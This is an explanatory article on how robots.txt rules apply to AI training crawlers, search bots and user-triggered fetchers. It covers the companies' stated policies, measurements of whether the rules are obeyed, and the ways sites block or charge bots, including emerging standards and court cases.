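This looks like a general ban with one exception. But Claude-User has a group of its own, so it never uses the general one, and its own group forbids nothing. It may therefore open every page on the site, including the members' area. The owner has to repeat the ban inside the second group:

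```
User-agent: Claude-User
Disallow: /
Allow: /castle/visit
```

Both rules now match `/castle/visit?month=december`. The `Allow` rule takes precedence because it is longer, at 13 characters to the `Disallow` rule's one, so Claude-User may open the page. The table shows which addresses each program may request under the two versions.

| Address | Claude-User, first version | Claude-User, corrected | GPTBot, both versions |
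|---|---|---|---|
| `/castle/visit?month=december` | Yes | Yes | No |
| `/castle/visitor-records` | Yes | Yes | No |
| `/members/list` | Yes | No | No |

The visitor records are still open to Claude-User because their address also begins with `/castle/visit`. The owner could mark the end of the address with a dollar sign after `visit`, but the rule would then no longer match the December page, because its address has a query string. The owner needs two rules, `Allow: /castle/visit$` and `Allow: /castle/visit?`, to cover the page with and without a query string and leave out the records.

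The same problem can occur later if the owner bans a new private folder in the general group, because that ban does not apply to any program that has its own group.

If the server answers a request for robots.txt with an error code between 400 and 499, such as 404 for a missing file, the program may request anything on the site. If the code is between 500 and 599, or the server doesn't answer at all, the program must assume that the whole site is off limits. If the failure lasts a long time, for example 30 days, the program may treat the file as missing or keep using an old copy. The difference makes sense because a 404 suggests that the owner never wrote any rules, while a crashed server may have rules that the program can't read.

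However, 403 ("forbidden") is also a code in the 400s. A firewall that refuses every request from a bot with a 403, including the one for robots.txt, therefore formally permits that bot to request anything. Anthropic warns site owners that blocking its IP addresses may not work as a lasting opt-out, because its bots then cannot read the file. An owner who uses a firewall can avoid this by letting requests for robots.txt through.

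Even a correctly written robots.txt file is only a request and can't block access. The file is also public, so a `Disallow` rule for a secret folder reveals that folder's path.

### Three kinds of bots

The robots.txt standard lets a site set different rules for different programs, but it doesn't cover what a company does with a page after fetching it. AI companies have partly made up for this by using separate names for separate purposes.

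| Company | Training | Search | User-triggered |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | GPTBot | OAI-SearchBot | ChatGPT-User |
| Anthropic | ClaudeBot | Claude-SearchBot | Claude-User |
| Perplexity | None listed | PerplexityBot | Perplexity-User |
| Google | Google-Extended | Googlebot | Google-Agent and others |

If the castle blocks GPTBot and ClaudeBot, OpenAI and Anthropic should leave its pages out of future training data. The block does not remove anything from existing models or stop ChatGPT or Claude from finding and quoting the site. specification.website's *robots.txt for AI crawlers* lists both limits among the points site owners often get wrong.

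A site that blocks the search crawlers loses readers. OpenAI says that a site that blocks OAI-SearchBot will not be shown in ChatGPT's search answers, although it can still appear as a plain navigational link. OpenAI's systems take about a day to adjust to a change in robots.txt. Anthropic says only that blocking Claude-SearchBot "may reduce" a site's visibility and accuracy in search results. A January 2026 BuzzStream study, cited by Search Engine Journal, found that 79% of top news sites blocked at least one training bot and 71% blocked at least one search or retrieval bot. Some of the sites that blocked search or retrieval bots may have wanted only to keep their content out of training.

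If the castle blocks Claude-User, Claude cannot open the castle's page when somebody asks about its Sunday hours in December. Claude may then answer from a travel site that lists last year's hours, so the block can make answers about the castle worse without reducing their number.

The names do not completely separate the purposes. If a site allows both GPTBot and OAI-SearchBot, OpenAI may use a single crawl for training and search. Google-Extended is a name that site owners can use in robots.txt to control what Google does with pages its ordinary crawlers have fetched. It covers training future Gemini models and grounding in Gemini Apps, which means giving the model pages from the search index while it answers. Sites therefore have no setting that lets them appear in Gemini's answers but stay out of its training data. Google-Extended does not affect Google Search or the AI summaries there,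 which have a separate control in Search Console, Google's service for site owners.

### What the companies have promised

The companies disagree mainly about user-triggered fetchers.

| Company | Written position on its user-triggered fetchers |
|---|---|
| Anthropic | They honor robots.txt |
| OpenAI | The rules "may not apply" |
| Perplexity | The rules generally do not apply |
| Google | They "generally ignore robots.txt rules" |
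| Microsoft | Promises to respect robots.txt when crawling, which does not settle the matter |

Anthropic says that all three of its bots honor robots.txt and do not try to get past CAPTCHAs, the puzzles that sites use to keep programs out. The bots also support `Crawl-delay`, an unofficial rule that lets a site ask bots to wait between requests. Anthropic also hosts browsers that Claude uses to complete tasks for people. These browsers use the name Claude-Agent, and Anthropic describes them on a separate help page, so a site owner cannot assume that the same promises cover them.

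OpenAI has moved away from its 2023 promise that ChatGPT-User would follow robots.txt. Its documentation originally presented robots.txt as the way to manage all three OpenAI bots. On December 9, 2025, OpenAI rewrote that passage to mention only OAI-SearchBot and GPTBot, and added that the rules may not apply to ChatGPT-User. According to PPC Land, marketing consultant Pieter Serraris noticed the edit.

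PPC Land concluded that ChatGPT-User would now ignore robots.txt, but OpenAI's wording is vaguer. In some ways it is less useful to site owners than a clear refusal to comply, because they cannot tell from the documentation whether a rule for ChatGPT-User will work for all requests, some or none.

Perplexity has taken a similar line for Perplexity-User, Search Engine Journal reports.

Google applies its policy to a long list of programs. Several have nothing to do with chatbots, such as those that fetch news feeds, make link previews for text messages, and read pages aloud. The list also includes Google-Agent, which navigates websites and performs actions at a user's request. TollBit (2026), a company that sells services to publishers, credits Google with making this agent easy to recognize. The agent has its own name and published IP ranges, and Google is experimenting with a cryptographic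 proof of identity. Site owners can therefore identify Google-Agent, but they need something stronger than robots.txt to block it.

Microsoft says that it respects robots.txt when it collects web pages for training. Since 2023 it has also let sites use tags to control what Copilot does with individual pages, which matters more to many publishers than whether a program requested them. According to Search Engine Journal, the NOARCHIVE tag keeps a page out of Copilot's answers, and NOCACHE limits Copilot to the page's address, title and snippet.

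### Is a fetch for a user the same as a visit?

Companies that exempt these fetchers from robots.txt argue that a person asked for the page. A browser doesn't check robots.txt when someone opens a link, and isn't expected to. People also use software to enlarge a page, translate it or read it aloud, and the site's owner has no say in that. An assistant that opens a page and explains it in simpler words can seem like a similar tool.

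The protocol's origin also supports this view. Koster and colleagues justify the rules by the inconvenience of crawlers visiting every address on a site, and a program that opens one page for one person causes no such inconvenience. Many owners presumably wrote their general bans with crawlers in mind. If fetchers obeyed those bans, owners would lose visitors they would have been happy to serve, such as a family planning a trip to the castle. Dark Visitors, a service that tracks bots, advises sites against blocking Perplexity-User because doing so in effect blocks the person using the assistant.

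Publishers reply that they earn money when people visit a page, but not when an assistant fetches it. A reader in a browser sees advertising, an offer to subscribe and links to other articles. The fetch tool keeps only the text, and the user reads the answer somewhere else. The Digital News Report found that few users go on to the source. Publishers have generally welcomed search crawlers because they bring visitors. Nottingham and Krishnan (2026) write in *Report from the IAB Workshop on AI-CONTROL* that some participants at a meeting of engineers, publishers and AI companies saw AI as hostile because it can take those visitors away.

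The number of fetches matters too. According to PPC Land, ChatGPT runs more than a billion searches a week. A newspaper loses almost nothing when one reader uses an ad blocker, but a company's decision about how its software treats robots.txt applies to all of its users at once. Publishers now also sell live access to their pages. According to Digiday's *WTF is the AI training opt-out policy token?*, this access has become central to most recent licensing deals between publishers and technology companies. An AI company that can fetch the same pages for free has less reason to sign such a deal.

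Publishers can also point out that the standard defines crawlers as "automated clients" and makes no exception for programs that a person has triggered. Cloudflare's *Perplexity is using stealth, undeclared crawlers to evade website no-crawl directives* treats following a site's directives as a basic norm for bots, and its complaint covered rules against both Perplexity-User and PerplexityBot. But the standard's own example of a crawler is a search engine's program that follows links from page to page, so the standard does not settle whether robots.txt applies to requests triggered by a person.

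The comparison with a browser is good if a user pastes an address and asks for a summary, because the user decided to visit that page. It is weaker if the user asks a general question and the assistant picks ten pages the user has never heard of, and weaker still if a scheduled task checks a site every morning while the user is asleep. In neither of those cases did the user decide to visit the site. The publishers' complaint about lost advertising applies in all three cases.

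The written policies don't distinguish between addresses the user supplied and pages the model chose. Google's exemption covers both a fetcher that requests only the addresses users have added to their research notebooks and Google-Agent, which navigates the web on its own. A company could instead ignore robots.txt for user-supplied addresses and obey it for pages the model chose. To prevent data leaks, assistants already track where an address came from, so this would not require much new software.

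Anthropic offers web browsing in Claude and promises to obey robots.txt. Claude therefore can't open some pages for its users that a competitor's assistant may open.

### Attempts at finer preferences

A castle's owner might be happy for assistants to quote its opening hours but not for anyone to train a model on its guidebook. Robots.txt can make this distinction only by naming bots, so the owner has to keep up with every company's list and add an entry for each new bot. *AI Bots and Robots.txt* (Calvano, 2025) reports that after OpenAI published instructions for blocking GPTBot in August 2023, the number of sites that mentioned it rose from zero to 578,000 by November.

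In September 2024, the Internet Architecture Board (IAB), which looks after the long-term design of the internet, held the workshop mentioned above. Participants listed several other weaknesses, and one remarked that "robots.txt is broken and we broke it". The site's administrator controls the file, so an author on a large platform may have no way to state a preference. If someone copies an article to another site, the original site's file doesn't cover the copy. A company reads the file when it crawls a page but may use the text years later, in a model from which a single source can't be removed.

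The last of these problems is much smaller for an assistant that fetches a page live, because it can read the preference when it uses the page. But the two sides first need shared terms for what the assistant is doing.

The IETF set up a working group on AI preferences to agree on a vocabulary for them. In May 2025 the group adopted a proposal from Open Future, a European digital policy organization, as its starting point, according to Open Future's *Divergent Mechanisms Elusive Vocabularies* (2026). By October the group had moved its deadlines from August 2025 to August 2026 and was considering categories based on what a system produces instead of what goes into it, according to Open Future's *IETF AI Preferences vocabulary* (2025). That month Cloudflare employees proposed their own categories in *Vocabulary For Expressing Content Signals* (2025). In April 2026 the group's draft covered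 only training and search, according to Astral's *What "Search" Means Is a Governance Decision* (2026).

The September draft, Keller and Thomson's *A Vocabulary For Expressing AI Usage Preferences* (2026), has three categories:

| Label | What it covers |
|---|---|
| `train-ai` | Using a page to change the learned parameters of a generative model |
| `ai-use` | Giving a page to a generative model as input, unless the user provided it directly |
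| `search` | Selecting pages and sending users to them, with a link and at most short excerpts |

The search category does not cover summaries, so when an assistant reads the castle's page and writes an answer with a citation, that is AI use, even if the company calls the product search. The group has not decided whether a user who gives the assistant an address has "directly" provided the page, which is much the same disagreement as the one about user-triggered fetchers. According to the draft, none of its contents reflect a consensus yet.

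A companion draft, Illyes and Thomson's *Associating AI Usage Preferences with Content in HTTP* (2026), adds a new kind of rule to robots.txt. The castle could write:

```
User-agent: *
Allow: /
Disallow: /members/
Content-Usage: train-ai=n, ai-use=y
```

`Allow` and `Disallow` would still determine which pages a program may fetch, and the last line would state what it may do with them. A site could also send the same preference in a header with each page, so a user-triggered fetcher that never reads robots.txt would still receive it. The rule would not apply to pages a company had already fetched until its crawler read the new file and fetched those pages again.

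### The training signal of October 2026

While the working group was still debating, Kevin Kelley of Anthropic submitted a simpler draft on October 30, 2026. OpenAI, Google and Microsoft announced on the same day that they planned to support it. It uses the existing format and introduces one special name, as in this example from the draft:

```
User-Agent: __usage_ai-training
Disallow: /
Allow: /press-kit/
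```

No bot has this name. The group records the site's objection to generative AI training on all its pages except the press kit, but it does not stop anyone from fetching those pages. The name contains only letters, hyphens and underscores, which the 2022 standard allows, so older software should treat it as the name of an unrecognized bot.

The usual rule about `*` does not apply here. Under the draft, a site without the new group has expressed no training preference, even if it bans all bots with `User-agent: *` and `Disallow: /`. This could surprise owners, as in the Claude-User example, though this time the general ban covers less than they think.

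The four companies also plan to treat the signal differently, as Search Engine Journal's *Google, Microsoft & OpenAI Plan To Honor Shared AI Training Opt-Out* explains:

| Company | Start | What happens alongside its existing controls |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Began October 30, 2026, with a gradual rollout | A rule that names ClaudeBot takes priority |
| OpenAI | "In the coming months" | It has not said what happens if a GPTBot rule conflicts |
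| Microsoft | February 1, 2027 | A tag or header on a single page overrides the signal |
| Google | Early 2027 | Counts as blocking Google-Extended, unless the site names that too |

A site that uses the signal to object to training will therefore also disappear from grounded answers in Gemini Apps, unless it sets Google-Extended separately. Microsoft treats training and grounding separately. It is adding a page-level setting for grounding, with an option that lets Microsoft's own products use a page but withholds it from other businesses that buy its grounding service.

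Microsoft will stop treating NOARCHIVE and NOCACHE as AI controls after March 1, 2027. Sites that rely on those tags to stay out of AI answers can record a temporary preference starting December 15. Otherwise, Microsoft will assume it may use their pages for grounding, at least until it crawls them again.

OpenAI says it will honor the signal for "foundational generative AI training". TechRadar's *Google and Microsoft among those signing up to OpenAI's plan* points out that this sounds narrower than the working group's definition, which covers any change to a generative model's parameters. Meta has welcomed the idea of a shared signal but has not committed to following it.

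Several publishers' representatives criticized the signal. Alex Springer, of the publishers' coalition SPUR, told Digiday that the companies were using their combined influence to impose a draft that nobody had reviewed. He also objected that training remains permitted until a site opts out. Paul Bannister of Raptive, an advertising company that works with publishers, called the signal "useless", partly because none of the four companies has promised not to buy the same text from others who scrape it.

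These objections are fair, but the signal lets the owner of a small site state one preference without keeping track of every company's list of bots, and existing rules for individual bots continue to work. Google argues that early support will help the eventual standard, and Kelley plans to offer the design to the working group as a change to the Content-Usage draft. For now it is one person's proposal, and it expires on May 3, 2027 unless a new version replaces it.

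The signal also doesn't restrict live browsing by ChatGPT-User or Claude-User, because an assistant that opens the castle's page to answer a question isn't training on it. The `ai-use` category would cover such visits, but the working group hasn't yet agreed on it, and its draft lets each company decide whether to follow the preference.

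## Whether robots.txt is obeyed and how websites enforce their choices

To find out whether a company's fetcher follows its written policy, someone has to compare a site's rules with the requests in its server log. Researchers, companies and site owners have done this in several ways since 2025, and their results for ChatGPT seem to contradict each other.

### What the server logs show

In *Scrapers selectively respect robots.txt directives*, Kim, Bock and colleagues (2025) studied how bots reacted to changes in a site's robots.txt. They had logs of about 3.9 million requests to 36 websites run by their university. On one busy site, they published three versions of the file for two weeks each. The first specified a delay between requests, the second allowed bots into only part of the site, and the third banned them from all of it.

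Bots generally complied less as the rules became stricter. Those that collect data for search engine optimization complied best, and ordinary search crawlers were among the worst. AI search crawlers rarely requested robots.txt.

ChatGPT-User did not fit this pattern. On a scale where 1 means full compliance, it scored 0.910 with the first version, 0.131 with the second and 1.000 with the third. A program that obeys a total ban should be able to obey a partial one, so the low second score is odd. It may reflect a small sample, since ChatGPT-User made only 3,029 visits to all 36 sites during the study.

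The researchers identified bots by the names the bots gave, and traced some of the apparent violations to impostors. The logs contained scrambled IP addresses to protect visitors' privacy, so the researchers could see which company's network a request came from but could not check the address against OpenAI's published list. Bots that pretend to be ordinary browsers are missing from the compliance scores.

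TollBit's figures come from many more sites, but nobody varied the robots.txt rules on them. Digiday's *European publishers are getting hit harder by AI bot scraping, report finds* reports a sample of 3,906 publishers for the first half of 2026, 456 of them European. On the European sites, about 15% of identified page fetchers reached addresses the site had disallowed, according to Search Engine Journal's *OpenAI Says Robots.txt May Not Apply To ChatGPT's Fetch Bot*. ChatGPT-User, ByteDance's Bytespider and Youbot each reached disallowed addresses on nearly half of the European sites that had named them in robots.txt.

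It is not clear whether the 15% refers to programs or to their requests. In its *State of the AI Bots* report for the second quarter of 2025, TollBit found that 13.26% of requests from AI bots bypassed robots.txt, up from 3.3% in late 2024. The 13.26% may not be comparable with the 15%.

TollBit, which publishes *State of the Bots*, also has a commercial interest in the problem because it sells publishers a paywall for bots and other access controls. That is no reason to dismiss its data, but the publishers it covers are not a random sample of the web. TollBit found that AI bots visited European sites more heavily than North American ones and ignored the European sites' rules more often. Cloudflare and the security company DataDome told Digiday that their traffic data did not show the same regional gap.

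A low number of violations can be misleading too, because, as PPC Land points out, a fetcher cannot violate robots.txt on sites that have no rule against it. Only 9% of the European sites disallowed Claude-User, compared with 26% in North America.

The third kind of measurement is much smaller. For Search Engine World's *Do AI Assistants Actually Respect Your robots.txt?*, testers created two unlinked pages for each of twelve assistants, one allowed by robots.txt and one disallowed. They pasted each address into the assistant's chat and asked for a summary and a secret reference number from the page. An assistant that returned the right number must have obtained the page.

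| Assistant | How its fetcher identified itself | Opened the disallowed page |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, Claude, Perplexity | By its own published name | No |
| Mistral | By its own published name | Yes |
| Gemini | By a general Google name | Yes |
| Meta AI | By a different name from the documented one | Yes |
| Copilot, Grok, DeepSeek, Qwen, Kimi | As an ordinary browser | Yes |
| ERNIE | By several names, some of them false | Yes |

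The allowed page was a sensible control because it showed that an assistant could open pages on the site. But this was a single round of tests on one site, with one disallowed page per assistant, so a temporary fault would have looked the same as obeying robots.txt.

Not all of the nine assistants that opened the page violated their developers' stated policies. Google's published policy, for example, exempts its user-triggered fetchers from robots.txt, and the testers had supplied each address themselves.

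The assistants' accounts of their visits were unreliable. Perplexity's reply was that it could not access a page its fetcher had just downloaded, so checking whether an assistant visited a site requires reading the server log.

### Why the results for ChatGPT differ

In a fourth study, *Fetch, Read, Reuse*, Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026) asked assistants about pages on two of their own sites from September to November 2026 and recorded every request. ChatGPT-User never requested robots.txt, while Claude-User had requested it within the hour before 99.9% of its page requests.

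| Measurement | Period | What it recorded | Result for ChatGPT-User |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kim and colleagues | Early 2025 | Compliance with three versions of the rules | 0.910, 0.131 and 1.000 |
| TollBit | January to June 2026 | Any request for a disallowed page | Violations on nearly half of the European sites that named it |
| Search Engine World | 2026 | One pasted link to a disallowed page | Did not open it |
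| Chen, Canini and colleagues | September to November 2026 | Whether it requested robots.txt | Never |

Timing may explain part of the difference, because Kim and colleagues collected their data before OpenAI weakened its promise in December 2025. But that cannot explain why two tests from 2026 disagree.

The definition of a violation matters more. Search Engine Journal notes that TollBit counts every request to a disallowed address as a violation, whatever the AI company says about its own fetcher. OpenAI would presumably regard many of these requests as permitted because users initiated them.

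TollBit's figure also counts sites instead of requests. If ChatGPT-User obeyed bans 999 times out of 1,000, a site that it was led to by 1,000 questions would still have about a 63% chance of recording at least one violation. "Nearly half of sites" is therefore consistent with a fetcher that usually obeys robots.txt or one that never checks it. A single test with one link, such as Search Engine World's, cannot distinguish these possibilities either.

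Chen, Canini and their colleagues conclude that OpenAI does not honor robots.txt, but their experiment does not establish this. Their sites allowed every bot, so they did not test whether OpenAI obeys a ban. OpenAI could in principle check a copy of the file collected by another of its crawlers. The researchers also reached ChatGPT-User through OpenAI's service for developers, whereas Search Engine World used the chat app, and the two may behave differently.

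The evidence for Claude is more consistent than for ChatGPT. Claude's fetcher read robots.txt in one study and obeyed it in the other, as Anthropic promises. It cached the rules for 60 to 70 minutes, so a new ban may not take effect for about an hour. Site owners can't rely on a ban to stop ChatGPT.

### What an obedient assistant misses

An assistant that obeys robots.txt loses access to some kinds of websites more than others. *Is Misinformation More Open?* (Steinacker-Olsztyn, Gosain and Dao, 2025) examined 3,369 reputable news sites and 710 misinformation sites, using labels from Media Bias/Fact Check, an organization that rates publishers' accuracy and political bias.

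Among sites with a valid robots.txt file, 60.0% of reputable sites completely banned at least one AI agent, compared with 9.1% of misinformation sites. The share of reputable sites with such a ban had risen from 23% in September 2023. Reputable sites named an average of 15.5 AI agents, while misinformation sites named 0.77.

News sites seem to keep track of how AI companies behave. In July 2024, a month after reports that Perplexity was ignoring robots.txt, 26 reputable sites that had allowed PerplexityBot to access some of their pages banned it entirely.

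A site may ban a training crawler and still admit an assistant's fetcher, so the 60.0% figure is not the share of reputable news sites lost to an assistant that obeys robots.txt. In May 2025, 45.1% of the reputable sites banned ChatGPT-User. Each AI agent was banned by fewer than 5% of the misinformation sites.

The researchers could reach 3,299 reputable sites and 672 misinformation sites, which made up about 17% of the total. If ChatGPT-User obeyed every ban, it would lose access to about 1,430 reputable sites and at most 25 misinformation sites. As a rough estimate, misinformation sites would then make up about 26% of the remaining sites.

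That estimate is an inference. Steinacker-Olsztyn and colleagues did not test any assistant's answers. An assistant does not choose among sites at random, and a search engine may rank most of the misinformation sites too low to matter. Licensing deals can also restore access to some publishers. The effect is probably largest for a question that only a few news sites have covered, where losing two of those sites may leave mostly poor sources. It would be smaller for Claude-User, which fewer sites ban.

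Despite this contrast, the two groups in the study blocked ClaudeBot, Anthropic's training crawler, at nearly the same rate. The researchers requested each site's homepage under an ordinary research name and then again as ClaudeBot. After accepting the first request, 24.8% of the reputable sites and 25.6% of the misinformation sites refused the second. Many misinformation sites that publish no ban against AI crawlers therefore block at least one of them. Some of their owners may not know it, since a hosting or security company can switch on such a block.

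### Blocking by name and address

A website's server can refuse a bot's request rather than rely on the bot to obey robots.txt. Sites have more reason to do this as AI bot traffic grows. TollBit counted one AI bot visit for every 31 human visits in late 2025, up from one for every 200 at the start of that year, according to TechRadar's *AI bot web traffic is closing in on human usage, experts warn*.

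The simplest way to block a fetcher is by its user agent. If the castle's server receives a request from `ChatGPT-User`, it can return a 403 error instead of the page. This stops a fetcher that identifies itself truthfully, even if its developer ignores robots.txt. But a fetcher can get past the block by using a different name, including the name of another fetcher that the site allows.

Checking the IP address against the company's published list catches most impostors:

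| Name in the request | IP address | Likely visitor |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT-User | On OpenAI's list | ChatGPT |
| ChatGPT-User | Not on OpenAI's list | An impostor |
| An ordinary browser | In a data center | A disguised bot, or a person using a VPN |
| An ordinary browser | At a home internet provider | A person, or a well-disguised bot |

A website can check a request's address against a company's list only if the company publishes one. Search Engine World could verify the addresses of ChatGPT and Perplexity this way, but found no published list for Claude. Claude's requests in *Fetch, Read, Reuse* came from networks belonging to Google and Amazon. A site that blocked those networks entirely would also block many unrelated services hosted on them.

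The fetcher in the last row of the table, which xAI uses for Grok, is the hardest to block. It sent 8,286 requests to the researchers' sites from 7,774 different addresses, and every request was labelled as coming from a browser on a Mac. When Chen, Canini and colleagues checked 100 of the requests by hand, 62 came from internet or phone providers. Blocking the addresses one by one would achieve little, because the next request would usually come from a new one. Blocking the providers would also shut out the human readers who use them.

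Sites can instead look for unusual behavior or make visitors solve a CAPTCHA puzzle. Kim and colleagues note that CAPTCHAs annoy people and that advances in AI have made them easy for programs to solve. They also mention tarpits, which feed a bot endless fake pages. A tarpit wastes a crawler's time, but a user-triggered fetcher might pass the fake text on to the user.

A mistaken block may also continue to affect an assistant after the site owner removes it. *Fetch, Read, Reuse* describes pages that first returned an error, such as a 403, and then worked normally. Claude's fetcher did not retry them during the test, which lasted up to about 11 hours, and Claude kept reporting that they were broken. ChatGPT's fetcher retried after about 25 minutes, but in 70% of those cases the answer still quoted the old error. If the castle's firewall briefly blocked Claude-User by accident on Sunday morning,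 Claude might spend the rest of the day unable to give the opening hours.

When sites block AI bots that identify themselves, demand often shifts to scrapers that evade detection, according to Akamai (2025), which sells protection against bots. An AI company can also use a scraper run by another company. In Search Engine World's test, Microsoft's Copilot got the disallowed page through Diffbot, a scraping company whose request looked like an ordinary browser's. TollBit (2026) keeps an index of such companies and says that many do not follow robots.txt by default.

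### Signed requests

A cryptographic signature can prove who sent a request without relying on a name or an IP address. The IETF is working on a standard for this. In outline, it works like this:

1. The bot's operator creates a pair of keys, keeps the private one secret and publishes the other on its own website.
2. The bot uses the private key to sign part of each request, including the name of the site and the time when the signature expires.
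3. The site, or a security company that protects it, obtains the public key and checks the signature.
4. If the signature is valid, the site applies its rule for that operator.

An impostor can copy the name `ChatGPT-User` but cannot produce a valid signature without OpenAI's private key. An attacker who copies a signature cannot use it on another site or for long, because it names the site and soon expires. Signatures also let an operator move to new servers without publishing a new list of addresses.

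Signed requests help a site admit bots it trusts much more than they help it detect other bots. A bot can still pretend to be a person by leaving its requests unsigned, because sites don't expect people's browsers to sign theirs. A signature also doesn't show what the bot will do with the page.

Signatures could also disadvantage newcomers. If large sites admit only signed bots from a list of approved operators, they may block a student's research crawler or a small open-source assistant, however well it behaves. Whoever keeps the list would have considerable power over who can build an assistant. Because a signature identifies the assistant with certainty, a malicious site could also use it for cloaking.

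### Cloudflare's new defaults

Cloudflare's network sits between visitors and more than 20% of web domains, so it can apply a block across all of them. On July 1, 2026, it announced separate controls for search bots, training bots and agents, according to PPC Land. Agents act for a person in real time. They include ChatGPT-User, as well as Claude or Gemini when they operate a Chrome browser.

Cloudflare has announced that it will block training bots and agents by default on pages with advertising, for domains that join from September 15, 2026. Search bots will still be allowed. Cloudflare treats an advertisement as a sign that the owner wanted a person to see the page.

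That is a reasonable guess for a newspaper but a poor one for many small sites. Suppose the castle opens a new website with one banner ad for a local hotel. The owner would probably like assistants to read the holiday opening hours. Until the owner changes the setting, however, the default keeps ChatGPT-User away from that page, so ChatGPT may give last year's hours without the owner knowing why.

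When a bot has several purposes, Cloudflare applies the strictest rule that covers any of those purposes. It named Googlebot, Applebot and BingBot as crawlers that combine search with training, and said it would block them for customers who choose to block training. A site whose owner only wants to keep text out of AI models could therefore disappear from ordinary search results. Cloudflare wants the companies to run separate crawlers for search and training. Existing customers could opt out of the change.

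Blocking AI crawlers may also reduce the number of people who visit a website. According to PPC Land, researchers at Rutgers and Wharton found that news publishers who blocked AI crawlers in robots.txt lost about 7% of their weekly traffic within six weeks. The decline also appeared in data on people's browsing, so the lost traffic wasn't all from bots.

Cloudflare can enforce its rules only against bots that it recognizes. It has proposed a header for requests that pass through another company, as Copilot's did through Diffbot. The header would identify the company the request is for and how that company will use the page. The intermediary has to fill in the header honestly. Cloudflare threatens that a bot caught abusing the system will lose its trusted status on every site that Cloudflare protects.

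### Charging for access

A site can charge a bot for access instead of refusing it. The server answers the request with the code 402, "Payment Required", and a price. A bot whose operator has an account can accept the price and request the page again. TollBit sells this kind of paywall, and Cloudflare has offered one too. *terms.txt* (2026), which proposes another payment system, describes robots.txt as "a preference signal being asked to do the work of a licensing system".

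Fetches are easy to count, but a price per fetch does not reflect how often assistants use a page, because OpenAI, Anthropic and xAI all keep a fetched page and use it to answer other customers' questions. *Fetch, Read, Reuse* found that OpenAI's copies lasted about 30 minutes. If all users shared one copy, OpenAI would fetch a page at most about 48 times a day, and at one cent per fetch the publisher would earn at most about 48 cents a day, whether 50 people or 50,000 asked about the page.

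A site can mark a page `no-store`, an instruction not to keep a copy. OpenAI and xAI ignored it in the tests. Anthropic's fetcher began following it on the researchers' own sites in mid-October 2026, but did not follow it consistently elsewhere.

Cloudflare has since moved towards payment for pages that contribute to an answer. This ties payment more closely to a page's value, but the publisher's log does not record answers, so the publisher has to trust the AI company's count or pay somebody to audit it.

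Either way, an assistant can decline to pay and use a free page instead. A newspaper with exclusive reporting still has some bargaining power, but the castle has almost none, because dozens of travel sites list its opening hours for free. Paywalls for bots could push assistants towards free copies of uncertain quality. They could also exclude researchers and small developers who cannot afford the fees.

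### Perplexity and the courts

The best-known accusation of disguised crawling came from Cloudflare in August 2025. *terms.txt* summarizes Cloudflare's claim that Perplexity used undeclared user agents and changing networks to fetch pages from sites that had disallowed its declared crawler. Cloudflare had set up new domains that banned all bots and then asked Perplexity about them, and Perplexity still described their contents. In the same test, ChatGPT read robots.txt and stopped. Cloudflare removed Perplexity from its list of verified bots.

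Perplexity replied that Cloudflare had confused its traffic with that of BrowserBase, a cloud browser service that Perplexity used only occasionally. It also argued that an assistant that opens a page for a user is not a crawler. Outsiders cannot check how much of the traffic was Perplexity's without both companies' logs. The second argument might justify ignoring robots.txt, but it does not justify hiding the assistant's name, because a site's operator needs to know who is visiting before deciding whether to accept the argument.

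Amazon made a similar complaint in November 2025, when it sued Perplexity over Comet, an AI browser whose agent can log in to a customer's Amazon account and shop there. Amazon said the agent was disguised as an ordinary Chrome browser and kept using its site after Amazon told Perplexity to stop. Perplexity answered that customers are allowed to choose software to shop for them.

In March 2026 a federal judge in California issued a preliminary order against Perplexity. She found that Amazon was likely to show that Comet had entered customers' accounts with their permission but without Amazon's. An appeals court temporarily suspended the order later that month. If other courts adopt the judge's reasoning, a user's consent will not be enough to authorize an agent that a site has expressly refused.

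The case is about accounts behind a password, so it does not settle whether an assistant may open public pages. In 2022, the same appeals court found, in a dispute between LinkedIn and the data company hiQ, that collecting data from public pages probably does not break the federal law against computer hacking.

Ziff Davis, the publisher of CNET and PCMag, sued OpenAI in 2025, partly on the ground that OpenAI's crawler had ignored the publisher's robots.txt files. US copyright law forbids getting around a technical measure, such as encryption, that effectively controls access to a work, and Ziff Davis argued that robots.txt was such a measure. A federal judge in New York dismissed that claim in December 2025, reasoning that robots.txt does not control access any more than a "keep off the grass" sign controls access to a lawn.

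The decision is consistent with the robots.txt standard on this point, but it does not make ignoring the file legal in every respect. Ziff Davis's claim that OpenAI infringed its copyright by copying articles was separate, and other courts need not follow the ruling. According to a legal analysis cited by Steinacker-Olsztyn and colleagues, violating robots.txt may still have legal consequences.

The EU's 2025 code of practice for general-purpose AI is voluntary, but companies that sign it commit to using crawlers that follow robots.txt. OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and Microsoft have signed. The commitment is in the code's rules on collecting training data, so it probably does not cover a page that ChatGPT-User opens to answer one person's question.
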